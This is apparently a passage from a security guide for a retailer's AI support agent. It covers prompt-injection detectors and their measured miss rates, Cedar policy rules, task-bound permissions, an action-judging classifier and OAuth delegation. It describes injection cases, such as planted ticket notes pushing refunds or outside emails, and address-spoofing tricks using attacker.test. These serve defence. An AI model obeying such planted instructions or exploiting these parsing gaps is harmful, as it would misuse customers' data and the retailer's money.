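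Flagging lets the text through and records the alarm. This suits the chat, where a false alarm would insult an honest customer, but it protects nobody unless something acts on the flag, whether a member of staff or a rule in the policy engine. A reasonable starting point for the retailer would be:

| Text | What to look for | After a hit |
|---|---|---|
| Customer's message | Jailbreak and direct injection | Flag and continue; block only very high scores |
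| Help article | Injection, when an employee saves it | Keep it out of search until somebody reads it |
| Tool result | Injection | Block it and pass the case to staff |
| Final reply | Harmful or confidential content | Replace it with a standard message |

### Measured detection rates

Liu's tests come closest to the retailer's situation. The first two used AgentDojo and τ-bench, which simulates customer service for a shop and an airline. To get harmless tool results, Liu ran the correct sequence of tool calls for each task without a language model. Liu then planted attacks from public benchmarks and ran the same calls again, labelling a result as injected if it differed from the clean version. A third test used BIPIA, a collection of emails, tables and programming answers with attacks inserted.

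The table lists each detector's false positive rate at its default threshold and its detection rate at a threshold that gives 1% false positives.

| Detector | False positives, AgentDojo | False positives, τ-bench | Detection, AgentDojo | Detection, τ-bench | Detection, BIPIA |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.7% | 82.2% | 100.0% | 37.7% |
| Wolf Defender | 0.9% | 0.0% | 73.8% | 90.8% | 3.5% |
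| Prompt Guard 2 (86M) | 0.6% | 0.0% | 69.4% | 57.9% | 10.4% |
| Prismor-1.5B | 6.5% | 46.2% | 72.2% | 15.2% | 4.0% |
| Sheltron | 10.6% | 4.4% | 20.1% | 95.2% | 57.2% |
| PIGuard | 29.5% | 11.0% | 2.1% | 52.7% | 95.1% |
| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 66.9% | 0.5% | 10.1% | 0.7% |

Prompt Guard 2 is the classifier in LlamaFirewall, Meta's open-source guardrail system. It rarely flags harmless results, but at the 1% setting it missed about 30% of the injections on AgentDojo and 42% on τ-bench. The two general-purpose judges caught 54% to 78% of the injections on these benchmarks, fewer than the best dedicated detectors.

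A detector's rank on one benchmark is a poor guide to its rank on another. The rank correlation between BIPIA and AgentDojo was 0.01, where 1 means the same order and 0 means no relation. False positive rates were more stable, with a correlation of 0.67 between the two agent benchmarks. So the retailer can learn something about false alarms from a published test on tool results, but it can't rely on the test's detection rate.

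Liu attributes the differences to the form of the training data. PIGuard's training data included 1,116 full BIPIA inputs, which explains its score on BIPIA. It also included 53 of the 62 attacks that Liu later planted in τ-bench, but as short prompts. When attacks appeared inside product names, PIGuard caught 52.1% of those in its training data and 55.8% of the others, so training on the wording gave it no advantage. Horizon-Labs' training data included none of the attacks, but it did include tool results with planted instructions, and the model scored highest on both agent benchmarks.

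The same effect explains an apparent contradiction with Waibl and colleagues, who found that PIGuard caught 92.1% of injections with only 0.3% false positives. Their injection datasets consist of prompts, not tool results. A buyer who chose PIGuard because of that result could use it for the chat, but would be disappointed with its performance on order records.

Even the best detectors in Liu's tests missed most injections that asked for an unrelated but harmless task. Missing these may matter less to the retailer than missing a request for money. Liu also chose where to plant the τ-bench attacks, and other detectors might do better if the attacks were planted elsewhere, such as in a seller's message. Liu did not test closed commercial services, so a company buying Prompt Shields has to test it on the company's own tickets.

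Liu calls the detection rates upper bounds because all of these attacks were fixed in advance. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), as summarised by Munirathinam, found that attackers who adapted to the defence defeated 12 published defences. A published detection rate therefore holds only for known attacks.

### Repeated attempts

Attackers can also simply try again. If each attempt has a 5% chance of passing the detector and the attempts are independent, the chance that at least one of ten succeeds is

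1 − 0.95^10 = 40%

Real attempts are not independent. Many classifiers give the same text the same score every time, so sending one message ten times is no better than sending it once. But an attacker who learns from each refusal can improve with every attempt. Targets also vary in difficulty, and a hundred attempts against a well-protected one may all fail for the same reason.

Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them, measured this effect on Claude Opus 4.5, an older Anthropic model. According to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, strong attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with a hundred. The simple formula, which treats attempts as independent, gives 38% for ten attempts and 99% for a hundred. It is roughly right for ten and far too high for a hundred, though 63% is still a high success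 rate for an attacker.

### The model's own resistance

The Gray Swan figures measure how often the model follows an injection in its input, not how often a detector catches one. A resistant model reduces the damage when the detector misses an injection.

In the July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5, Anthropic reports that attacks on the model succeeded 0.2% of the time on one attempt and 2.0% within 15 attempts. The test used 1,130 attacks from a public competition, chosen because they worked on several models. Attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol, OpenAI's most capable model in the comparison, succeeded 3.1% of the time on one attempt and 20.0% within 15. Anthropic has an interest in the outcome of the comparison, and the attacks did not adapt to the model under test.

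Anthropic also used an automated attacker that had refined its methods on earlier models. It made 200 attempts in each of 40 coding scenarios. Against Opus 5 with extended reasoning, 0.56% of attempts succeeded, but the attacker succeeded at least once in 13 scenarios. If every attempt had had the same independent chance, it would have succeeded in about 27 scenarios, so the successes must have been concentrated in the weaker ones. For the retailer, one kind of ticket can succeed repeatedly as an attack even when the average success rate is low.

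When Anthropic added detectors that inspect tool results, the attack success rate fell to 0.18% and the number of broken scenarios to four. With the same detectors, Claude Mythos 5's rate fell only from 0.45% to 0.41%, and its number of broken scenarios rose from eight to 11. Anthropic reports that improved safeguards cut the success rate from 8.0% to 1.4% in browser tests of the older Opus 4.5.

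Newer models have mostly kept these gains in injection resistance. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, released in September, reports that the model performed similarly to Opus 5 or better on every injection test reported. The model also refused the smallest share of malicious requests among the models tested, so resistance to planted instructions doesn't guarantee resistance to a malicious user.

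Retailers often choose a cheaper model for customer support, and these figures may not apply to it. Help Net Security's *Anthropic's new budget model gets much better at ignoring hidden commands* (2026) reports that Claude Haiku 5.5 was less resistant to prompt injection than Sonnet 5.5 and Opus 5.5 on a Gray Swan benchmark. Most of Haiku's remaining weakness was in operating graphical interfaces, which the support agent doesn't do.

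### How a failing detector shows itself

Too many false alarms are easy to notice because the agent tells customers it can't open their tickets, and cases pile up with staff. The retailer should count blocked conversations as well as flagged results, since a modest false-alarm rate per result can block a large share of conversations.

A sudden rise in alarms often has a technical cause. Sheltron accepts a label for a text's source. When Liu labelled harmless τ-bench results "other" instead of "tool_result", the false positive rate rose from 4.4% to 85.6%. A change in the ticket software's export format could have a similar effect. Before assuming an attack, staff should check whether the rise began with a software update and whether the flagged texts contain any instructions.

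It is also suspicious if alarms suddenly stop. If the agent reads 1,000,000 tool results a month and the false positive rate is 0.1%, the retailer should see about 33 false alarms a day. A day with none probably means the detector has stopped receiving text or the application records a timeout as a score of zero. Sending a known injection through the system every day will reveal either fault sooner.

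Missed attacks leave no such trace. In the base-rate example, five injections remain among roughly 990,000 unflagged results. If staff read 1,000 of these at random, they have about a 0.5% chance of finding one. They will learn more by working backwards from effects. When the policy engine refuses an email to an unknown address and the detector has flagged nothing in that session, somebody should read every text the agent received before it tried to send the email. Permitted refunds produce no refusal to investigate, so the retailer has to look for patterns in the payments, such as a cluster of $300 refunds on orders from one marketplace seller.

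## Writing rules for tool calls and their arguments

A policy engine can refuse an email to an unknown address only if someone has written a rule that distinguishes known addresses from unknown ones. Amazon Bedrock AgentCore, a service from Amazon Web Services (AWS) for running agents, is a useful example of how such rules work because AWS documents it in detail, often using a $500 refund limit to illustrate. Its policy component became generally available in March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). Developers write the rules in Cedar, an open-source language that AWS designed for authorization. They can also use Dogwood, a newer language that, according to AWS's *Policy authoring guide*, accepts every valid Cedar policy.

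### From a tool call to a decision

AgentCore's gateway is the enforcement point. It sits between the agent and its tools, so when the model proposes the $64 refund for the kettle, the call stops there. The gateway also receives a signed token that identifies the customer. AWS's *Policy Overview* shows how the gateway combines the two into a request with four parts:

| Part | Question it answers | For the kettle |
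|---|---|---|
| Principal | Who is asking? | The signed-in customer's account |
| Action | Which tool? | `issue_refund` |
| Resource | Through which gateway? | The retailer's support gateway |
| Context | With what arguments? | Order 48213, 6,400 cents, 12 days old |

The engine compares the four parts with its rules, and the gateway forwards the call to the payment system only if the engine returns "allow".

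The amount is in whole cents because Cedar has no floating-point numbers. AgentCore converts an argument of the general type "number" into a fixed-point decimal, and a test reported on the blog chaosreload showed that such an argument must arrive as 500.0, because the engine treats a plain 500 as a different type. Using whole cents avoids this problem because every amount is an integer.

The order's age has to come from the retailer's order database, not from the model. But a 90-day rule in AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* reads the order date from the tool's arguments, which the model fills in. Under the limits in AWS's *Schema constraints*, a rule can't query a database. So the retailer's software has to look up the order and write its age into the call before the call reaches the gateway, overwriting the model's value.

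### The refund rule and three calls

With AgentCore's long identifiers shortened, the retailer's rule becomes two Cedar policies:

```
permit (
  principal is OAuthUser,
  action == Action::"issue_refund",
  resource == Gateway::"support"
)
when {
  context.input.amount_cents > 0 &&
  context.input.amount_cents < 50000
};

forbid (
  principal,
  action == Action::"issue_refund",
  resource
)
when { context.input.days_since_order > 90 };
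```

`OAuthUser` is AgentCore's type for a caller who signed in through OAuth, a common login standard. The `permit` policy allows refunds above zero and below $500. The `forbid` policy blocks any refund on an order more than 90 days old. Here is how the engine handles three proposed refunds:

| Proposed refund | Does the permit match? | Does the forbid match? | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| $64, order 12 days old | Yes | No | Allow |
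| $450, order 120 days old | Yes | Yes | Deny |
| $500, order 12 days old | No | No | Deny |

Cedar blocks the $450 refund, even though it is within the limit, because one matching `forbid` overrides any number of matching permits. It refuses the $500 refund by default because neither policy matches it.

The exact limit is worth testing because people often state limits carelessly in prose. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* states a requirement of "$500 or less" and then implements it as `amount < 500`, which refuses a refund of exactly $500. AWS's refund examples also have no lower bound, so a refund of minus $50 would satisfy them. Depending on the payment system, that might produce an error or charge the customer.

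The two policies still don't check that the order belongs to the customer, and that check has to use facts the model cannot alter.

### Why the order of the rules doesn't matter

Cedar reaches every decision by the same formula, in which each P is a permit policy that may match and each F is a forbid policy:

allow = (P₁ or P₂ or …) and not (F₁ or F₂ or …)

If no permit matches, the first bracket is false and the engine refuses the call. The order of the policies inside a bracket doesn't affect the decision. Many firewalls, by contrast, stop at the first matching rule, so moving a rule can open or close access by accident. With Cedar, the retailer's finance team can add a `forbid` without knowing what the support team has written, and no later permit can override it.

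This is also why forbids are useful in a system that already refuses everything by default. AWS's *Writing policies in natural language* explains that they protect against later permits that are too broad. In an emergency, the retailer can stop all tool calls with a single unconditional `forbid`, a pattern from AWS's *Common policy patterns*.

However, an exception to a forbid can be mistaken for a permit. Suppose the retailer adds `unless` to the 90-day forbid to exempt orders with an extended warranty. This only lifts the prohibition for those orders. A refund on one of them still needs a matching permit, so $600 remains too much.

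Cedar has no loops, so evaluation always ends, and a badly written rule can't leave a customer waiting forever. According to AWS, evaluation usually takes linear time, meaning that twice the work takes about twice as long. But a policy can't store anything between calls, so plain Cedar can't count refunds. It allows a fifth refund of $499 just as it allows the first, unless the retailer adds rules that depend on earlier calls.

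The gateway also uses the policies before the model proposes a tool call. When the agent requests the list of tools, the engine evaluates the policies with the arguments left blank to find tools they would block in every case, and the gateway leaves those tools off the list. If the retailer's server also offers `delete_account` and no permit covers it, the model never reads its name or description. `issue_refund` stays on the list because the policies allow some refunds.

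A planted note could give an agent the name of a hidden tool, so AWS's claim that an agent can't try to use a tool it doesn't know exists is too strong. The protection comes from the gateway, which would refuse the call. Hiding the tool mainly saves the model from wasted attempts.

### Checking arguments

A permitted tool can do a lot of damage with the wrong arguments, and text arguments are harder to check than amounts. Suppose the agent is allowed to email the retailer's courier at `courier.example`. AWS's guide to writing policies in English gives "when the email contains @example.com" as a sample condition. A similar rule for the courier would accept `claims@courier.example`, but also `claims@courier.example.attacker.test`, which is on someone else's domain.

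According to AWS's *Limitations*, Cedar has no regular expressions and can match patterns only with `*` wildcards, so it's a poor tool for taking addresses apart. An allow-list of complete addresses is safer:

`["claims@courier.example", "returns@courier.example"].contains(context.input.to)`

An exact comparison works only if both sides are in the same form. Cedar treats `Claims@Courier.Example` and `claims@courier.example` as different strings, although nearly every mail system delivers them to the same mailbox. This mismatch makes an allow-list block a legitimate email, but it would make a list of forbidden addresses let a bad one through. This is a good reason to prefer allow-lists, which refuse any spelling they don't contain.

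Before passing an email address to the engine, the retailer's software should check that the field contains only one, remove spaces and any display name, and convert the rest to lower case. For links, it should extract the host, the part of a web address that identifies the server. `https://courier.example@attacker.test/` looks like a link to the courier, but browsers treat everything before the @ as login details and go to `attacker.test`. Stacklok's *Authorization policy reference* describes a similar step in another Cedar-based gateway, which identifies each data resource by a sanitized address.

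The tool must then receive the same cleaned value that the engine checked. If the engine approves a cleaned copy and the email function gets the original, the two may parse the address differently, and the message can go to a recipient the engine never approved.

Optional arguments are easy to forget. If `send_email` accepts a `cc` field, a rule that checks only `to` lets the agent copy in anyone. Cedar's `has` operator tests whether an argument is present, so the retailer can forbid every call where `context.input has cc`. Removing the field from the tool would be simpler. The `to` field could be removed too. Most support emails go to the customer, so `send_email` could take a ticket number and look up the address itself, so the model doesn't have to supply one. Emails to the courier could use a separate tool with the allow-list.

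Numeric limits need a unit and sometimes a currency. If the tool takes dollars but the rule is in cents, a limit of 50,000 allows refunds of up to $49,999. A retailer that also sells in Britain has to decide whether 499 means dollars or pounds.

The order total is a better limit for refunds. The retailer's software already looks up the order's age and can look up the total at the same time. The permit then needs one more condition, `amount_cents <= order_total_cents`. This would stop the agent from refunding $499 for a $64 kettle and catch the mistaken entry of $94 that the fixed limit lets through.

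A rule can't establish that a value the model supplied is true by comparing it with other values. One of AWS's sample rules gives a bulk discount except on limited-edition products, and it takes the product types from the model's tool call. If the model leaves "limited edition" out of the list, the rule grants the discount.

### Proving things about a set of rules

Because Cedar policies have no loops or memory, a program can translate them into logical formulas and prove facts about every possible request instead of trying examples. AgentCore runs this analysis when it drafts policies from a developer's plain-English description, and again when the developer attaches policies to a gateway.

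AWS gives the example of a shop with gold and platinum customers. A `permit` policy allows refunds under $100 to gold customers. A `forbid` policy blocks refunds under $500 to gold and platinum customers. Each looks reasonable alone. For a gold customer's refund of a dollars, they combine into

allow = (a < 100) and not (a < 500)

The permit can never take effect because it covers only refunds below $100, and the forbid blocks every refund below $500. For refunds of $100 or more, no permit matches and the default deny applies, so gold customers get no refunds at all. The policy writer probably meant to forbid refunds *above* $500, but the analysis can't detect that intent. It describes the conflict, AgentCore rejects the change, and a person has to decide which policy is wrong.

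The same method finds a permit that matches nothing because it requires a customer to be gold and platinum at once, and one that matches everything because it accepts quantities of at least 100 or below 100. A developer can override such findings with the setting `IGNORE_ALL_FINDINGS`, which a sample command in AWS's *Test a policy in LOG_ONLY mode* uses when creating a policy.

AWS also offers a tool that compares two versions of a rule set. In its example, a discount rule excludes limited-edition products, and a developer changes it to exclude them only when the order exceeds 200 items. The tool reports the new version as more permissive, even though the added condition looks stricter, because it allows an order for 73 limited-edition items that the old version refused. This comparison may be the most useful check for the retailer. A refund limit mistyped as 500,000 cents contains no contradiction,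 so only a careful reader or a comparison with the previous version would reveal it.

### Rules written for one task

Fixed rules stay the same whatever the user asks for. If a customer asks only where a parcel is, but an attacker has planted a request for a $300 refund in the ticket, the refund rule still permits the payment. A task-bound permission covers only what the customer's request needs, so it would not include `issue_refund`.

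Nobody can write such rules by hand for every customer, so *Progent* (Shi, He et al., 2025) has a language model write them. The model drafts a policy from the user's request and revises it as tool results arrive. For the kettle refund, the draft might let the agent read ticket 7731 and order 48213 and refund that order. Once `get_order` returns the price, the model can limit the refund to $64.

The ticket may also contain a planted note that leads the model to add permission to email an outside address. Progent therefore checks each policy revision with an SMT solver, a program that decides whether a set of logical conditions can be satisfied. If the new policy only removes permissions, it takes effect at once. If it would allow any new call, it needs approval first, so an injection can't expand the model's permissions by itself.

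In Shi and colleagues' tests, Progent cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%, and only 6% of the revisions needed approval. On the Agent Security Bench benchmark, it cut the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. Competing researchers tested Progent with GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, and measured higher rates of 9.4% on AgentDojo and 15.8% on Agent Security Bench. Differences in the model or in Progent's version could explain the gap.

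*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that hostile text in a tool result may lead Progent to relax its own rules. The approval step prevents this if somebody uses it properly. But Progent also has a setting that approves every expansion automatically, and the objection holds when that setting is on.

A more basic problem for the retailer is that Progent derives the rules from the user's request, and the user may be the attacker. A customer who dishonestly asks for a $450 refund gets a policy that allows it. The customer can't approve expansions either, so the 6% would go to staff. Generated rules therefore have to operate inside the fixed ones, and Progent supports permanent rules for this purpose.

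Conseca, another research design, also has a model write a policy for each task and leaves enforcement to ordinary code. It shows the policy-writing model only the request and context that the developer trusts, so a planted note can't influence the rules. This also prevents the model from using helpful information in the ticket when it writes the rules.

How much does it cost to fix the rules before the agent has read anything? Li, Liu and colleagues (2025), in *DRIFT*, measured this on AgentDojo. Their system, DRIFT, first plans the sequence of tool calls and lists the expected arguments for each. If the agent departs from the plan, a second model decides whether the new call fits the user's request. A third component masks instructions in tool results that conflict with the request. The researchers added these parts one at a time to an agent running on GPT-4o-mini:

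| Setup | Tasks completed without an attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 63.6% | 30.7% |
| Plan only | 43.2% | 2.1% |
| Plan, with departures reviewed | 58.5% | 5.4% |
| Plan, review and masking | 57.3% | 1.4% |

The unchangeable plan stopped most attacks, but it also stopped the agent from completing about a third of the tasks it could otherwise complete. Success fell sharply on tasks that needed three or more calls, and the kettle task needs four. Allowing reviewed departures from the plan recovered most of the lost tasks but let more attacks succeed. On AgentDyn, a harder benchmark of open-ended tasks, every defence that Li and colleagues tried performed poorly, including DRIFT.

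DRIFT automatically approves any unplanned call that only reads data. That may suit an assistant working through its owner's files, but at the retailer a read can expose another customer's order, so the fixed rules still have to cover reads.

### A model that judges each action

The remaining option is to write no rule for a call and let a model decide whether to allow it. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, normally asks the user before it runs a command, but users approve nearly everything. In its "auto mode", a classifier built on a language model makes most of these decisions instead.

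Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes how auto mode checks an agent's actions. Fixed rules first let through safe actions, such as reading files. For most other actions, a classifier makes a quick yes-or-no decision that leans towards blocking. If the decision is to block, the classifier checks the action again with longer reasoning. Its input includes the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but never the tool results or the agent's explanations. Instructions planted in a tool result therefore can't reach the classifier directly, and the agent's explanations can't lead it to approve a bad command.

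The classifier blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to leak data and 17% of 52 real cases in which the agent had gone beyond what the user wanted. Because there were only 52 real cases, the true miss rate for such cases could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but accepted weak evidence of consent. For example, when a user asked the agent to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), the classifier treated this as permission to overwrite the project's history.

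Newer results are better, though they come from easier cases. In Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), 1,053 paid testers each received one clearly dangerous command among their approval requests. The testers blocked 13.6% of these commands and auto mode blocked 89%. The testers' rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more requests. This is strong evidence for using the classifier instead of a tired human, but not for using it instead of a refund rule, which blocks every $5,000 refund that reaches it.

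A model is most useful as a judge where the fixed rules provide no basis for a decision. If a customer has asked only about a parcel and the agent proposes a $300 refund, a judge model given both the request and the proposal can detect that nobody asked for the refund. But customers can't authorize spending the retailer's money the way developers can authorize changes to their own code. When a customer does demand a refund, the judge can easily mistake the demand for permission.

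Fixed rules are predictable, and people can read, test and analyse them, but they ignore the purpose of the conversation. Generated rules follow the task and still give a definite answer to each call, although a model may have drafted them badly. A judge needs no rule for a situation that nobody foresaw, and it misses some dangerous actions. The retailer can use all three if it combines them with "and":

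allow = fixed rules permit it and task rules permit it and the judge does not object

A mistake by either model can then block a legitimate refund, but it can't allow a refund that the fixed rules don't permit. Claude Code is less strict, since its classifier can approve actions that no fixed rule covers. The retailer could start with the fixed rules alone and add a judge only for refunds and outgoing emails, where a permitted call can still do harm.

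### How rules fail, and what the logs show

Some faults in the rules block too much. If the retailer adds a `track_parcel` tool but forgets to write a permit rule for it, AgentCore's gateway hides the tool from the agent. The log then contains no calls to the tool, and customers soon complain that the agent can't find their parcels.

A missing restriction is harder to notice. If nobody limits the recipients of `send_email`, the log shows ordinary approvals. A rule that permits everything produces a similar log, except that one policy matches every approved call and only forbid rules, such as the 90-day limit, still cause denials. Keycard, an access-control service that follows Cedar's logic, ships with such a rule, a default policy that lets every authenticated user reach every resource. Its engine denies requests by default, but this has no effect on users' requests until the customer replaces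 that policy.

The worst case is an engine that allows every action when it has no policies. Microsoft documents this behavior for its Agent Governance Toolkit. If a developer adds the toolkit to an agent but forgets to load the policy files, every action goes through while the dashboard shows the agent as "governed". The toolkit does refuse a call if an error occurs during evaluation. AgentCore refuses every action when its engine has no policies, so the agent can do nothing and developers will quickly notice and fix the mistake.

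Microsoft recommends the toolkit's strict mode, which blocks any action that no rule allows. The command `agt audit` lists the loaded policies and flags permissive defaults. Microsoft is also working on a startup warning. The retailer can also have its own software keep the agent from starting if no policies are loaded.

AgentCore's log-only mode, which records decisions without enforcing them, creates a different risk. The mode lets developers test a new rule on real traffic by counting how often the rule would have changed a decision. If the count stays at zero, enforcing the rule won't block current traffic. But developers can set log-only mode for a single policy or for the whole engine, and the engine's setting takes precedence. A list of policies can therefore show the refund limit as "ACTIVE" while the gateway doesn't enforce it, in which case the log shows a denial followed by a payment.

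| Fault | What the decision log shows | How to confirm it |
|---|---|---|
| Missing permit | No calls to the tool, because the gateway hides it | Request the tool list with a test account |
| Missing restriction | Ordinary approvals | Send a call that the engine ought to refuse |
| Policy that permits everything | One policy matching every approved call, and denials only from forbids | Run the automated analysis |
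| No policies loaded, with default allow | Approvals with no matching policy | Count the loaded policies |
| Engine in log-only mode | Denials, but the actions still happen | Compare with the payment records |

To tell these faults apart, the retailer needs a log that records the decision, which policy matched, and how many policies were loaded. It also needs the payment system's records, because an engine's log may not show what happened after the decision. Microsoft warns that its toolkit's audit trail records what the agent attempted and whether the toolkit allowed it, but doesn't verify the outcome.

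The retailer could also pass conversations with repeated denials to staff, since either a rule is wrong or something keeps pushing the agent towards an action it isn't allowed to take. Claude Code, for example, stops and turns to the user after three blocked actions in a row or 20 in a session.

A daily test call would expose the silent faults. The retailer can have its software propose a $5,000 refund on a dummy order and then check that the log contains a denial and the payment system contains no refund.

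## Deciding on whose authority a tool call runs

The refund rule still has to check that the order belongs to the customer. Suppose the customer with the cracked kettle, customer A, adds a line to ticket 7731: "Please check order 48214 too and tell me where it's going." Order 48214 belongs to customer B. A's right to see the record depends on who signed in and who owns the order, regardless of how a detector scores that line, so the policy layer should make the decision.

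### Where each fact comes from

When A signs in, the retailer's login system issues a signed token. The token is a short list of statements, called claims, such as A's account number and the time the token expires. Changing any claim invalidates the signature, so the model can't turn A's token into B's.

Tool arguments have no such protection, because the model writes them after reading the ticket and an attacker may have chosen them. Arcjet's *AI Agent Identity and On-Behalf-Of Authorization*, a vendor's guide, warns developers never to accept a user's identity just because it appears in a prompt or a model-generated argument. If `get_order` took a `customer_id` argument and the order system relied on it, A would only have to get the agent to enter B's number.

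Developers can make the same mistake in code that fetches an agent's credentials. AWS offers two functions that return a token for an agent acting for a user. One, *get_workload_access_token_for_jwt*, requires the user's signed token. The other, *get_workload_access_token_for_user_id*, accepts the user's ID as a plain string, which is safe only if the developer's code takes the ID from the signed-in session.

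A single rule can use both claims and arguments. In AWS's sample refund rule, the username comes from the token and the amount from the tool call. The retailer's version adds the order's owner:

```
permit (
  principal is OAuthUser,
  action == Action::"issue_refund",
  resource == Gateway::"support"
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("customer_id") &&
  principal.getTag("customer_id") == context.input.order_owner &&
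  context.input.amount_cents > 0 &&
  context.input.amount_cents < 50000
};
```

| Value | Who supplies it | Can a planted note change it? |
|---|---|---|
| `customer_id` | The login system, in the signed token | No |
| `amount_cents` | The model | Yes |
| `order_owner` | The retailer's software, from the order database | Only by making the model pick another order |

The model can safely supply the amount because it is only a proposal. If the model enters $64, the rule checks that figure before the payment system pays it. The order's owner is a fact that the model could get wrong, so the retailer's software has to supply it, as it does the order's age.

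This policy has to replace the earlier refund permit, which would otherwise still allow refunds on anyone's order. `get_order` needs the same ownership condition.

Many systems check less than this. Tokens often contain scopes, broad permissions such as `orders:read`, which both A and B would have. AuthZed, another vendor, points out that scopes can't determine access to individual records. Roles have the same limit. In an example from Teleport, Alice asks her agent to update order 42, and the gateway blocks the call because her role doesn't include the update tool. Bob's role does include it, but that check doesn't cover which orders he may update.

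### Three ways to give the agent access

The ownership rule can't protect order 48214 from a call that bypasses the gateway. The order system can make its own check, but only if the call identifies the requester, which depends on whose identity the agent uses.

The simplest arrangement is a shared service account. The agent logs in as itself for every customer, and its account can read every order. The application's code is supposed to add a filter to each query. AWS's *Propagate user authorization context in AI agents with Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* calls this a single point of failure, because one bug or successful injection can expose the whole dataset. According to TrueFoundry's documentation, a tool called this way receives no claims about the user, so it can't make per-user decisions. TrueFoundry also warns against falling back to a default user when the claims are missing.

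Alternatively, the agent can present A's own token. The order system then refuses to show order 48214, because A couldn't open it on the website either. But the token also covers everything else A can do, such as changing a delivery address or closing the account. The internet standard *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, 2020) calls it impersonation when the receiving system can't distinguish the agent from the user. HKU SPACE AI Hub's *Implement on-behalf-of token exchange for multi-tenant agents with Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Gateway* warns that forwarding the token unchanged turns every tool that receives it into a confused deputy. If the agent sent A's token to the courier's server, for instance, the courier could use it to log in to the retailer as A.

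The third arrangement gives the agent a separate identity and limits each call to the overlap:

allowed = what the customer may do ∩ what the agent may do

Customer A may read their own orders, change their address and close their account. The agent may read orders and tickets. The overlap between these permissions includes reading A's orders, but excludes reading B's orders and changing A's address.

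If the gateway's ownership rule is missing, the request for order 48214 turns out as follows:

| Arrangement | Order system's response | What a thief could do with the credential | Who appears in the log |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shared service account | Returns B's order | Read every order | The agent |
| Customer's own rights | Refuses | Anything A can do | Customer A |
| Overlap | Refuses | Read A's orders and tickets | The agent, acting for A |

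Refunds don't fit the formula as well. In AWS's example, Sales and Finance employees already have rights to the data they ask about. A customer has no right to take money out of the retailer's account, so requiring a strict overlap of permissions would rule out every refund. The retailer has to pay on its own authority and use the customer's identity only to decide which orders qualify.

The overlap also protects less when the user has wide access. If a staff member tells the agent to deal with ticket 7731, the principal is the staff member, who is allowed to read every order. Both sets of rights then include order 48214, and A's line in the ticket can still get B's address into the reply. To stop this, the retailer must also require that the order belong to the customer on the ticket.

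An emailed ticket that the agent processes overnight has no signed-in user, and anyone can forge the sender's address. The agent can answer general questions, but it should ask the customer to sign in before it opens an order.

### Exchanging one token for another

For the overlap to work, the order system needs proof of both identities. OAuth token exchange can supply it. In the retailer's case, the exchange would work like this:

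1. The gateway receives A's token along with the agent's proposed call to `get_order`.
2. It sends A's token to the authorization server, the service that issues tokens, as the "subject token". It adds the agent's own token as the "actor token" and names the order system as the target.
3. The gateway also proves its own identity. Without this step, anyone who stole A's token could trade it for others.
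4. The authorization server validates both tokens and applies its policy. A's token may include a `may_act` claim that lists who can act for A.
5. The server issues a new token for the order system, which checks it before returning anything.

The new token might contain these claims:

```
{
  "iss": "retailer-login",
  "aud": "order-system",
  "sub": "customer-A",
  "act": { "sub": "support-agent" },
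  "scope": "orders:read",
  "iat": 1791331200,
  "exp": 1791331260
}
```

Here `sub` identifies the customer, `act` the agent and `aud` the only system that should accept the token. The token expires 60 seconds after issue, as in the standard's example. If the agent passes the work to another agent, the claims can also list the earlier agents, but Jones and colleagues say that only the current one may affect the access decision.

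The gateway should request a separate token for each system. If it requests one token with two scopes for two systems, it is asking for both scopes on both systems. For example, a gateway that needs to read orders in one system and pay refunds in another could also be asking for permission to pay refunds through the order system.

The token exchange standard leaves calculating the overlap to the authorization server's policy and makes the actor token optional. AWS promises a narrower token that carries both the user's identity and the agent's in its April 2026 announcement, *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Identity now supports On-Behalf-Of (OBO) token exchange*. But in AWS's worked example with Salesforce, the developer sets the actor token to "None", so the exchange supplies no separate token for the agent. Salesforce still applies the employee's own access rules, which prevent the agent from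 fetching another department's records. A retailer that wants the agent's name in its logs should inspect a real token before relying on the feature.

Systems also record the agent in different formats. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) describes how this inconsistency forces developers to rely on proprietary conventions, and proposes a common format. The proposal is an individual draft that expires on 29 October, so the order system may need custom code to read the `act` claim for now.

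### The Model Context Protocol's rules

The Model Context Protocol has its own authorization rules, based on OAuth. The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), the version of 28 July, sets out this sequence for a server reached over the web:

1. The client, here the retailer's chat application, calls the server without a token. The server refuses, and tells the client where to find its authorization details and which scopes it needs.
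2. The client finds the right authorization server and opens a browser so that the user can sign in and consent. Its request identifies the tool server that will receive the token, and includes a value derived from a secret that the client has just created.
3. The authorization server sends back a code. If the response identifies its issuer, the client checks that against the issuer it expected.
4. The client trades the code and the secret for an access token. Somebody who intercepts the code can't use it without the secret.
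5. The client attaches the token to every request, and the server checks each time that it is the intended recipient.

*Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) reports that the July revision began requiring clients to check the issuer when the response includes one. This check prevents a malicious authorization server from getting the client to hand over a code that an honest server issued.

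The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) forbids servers from accepting tokens meant for another service or passing on the client's token. If a tool server needs to call another system, it must use a separate token from that system's authorization server. Token exchange can provide one without the customer having to consent again.

The protocol's authorization rules are optional, and servers that run on the same machine as the agent take credentials from their environment instead. So the retailer can't assume that a tool server checks tokens just because it uses the protocol.

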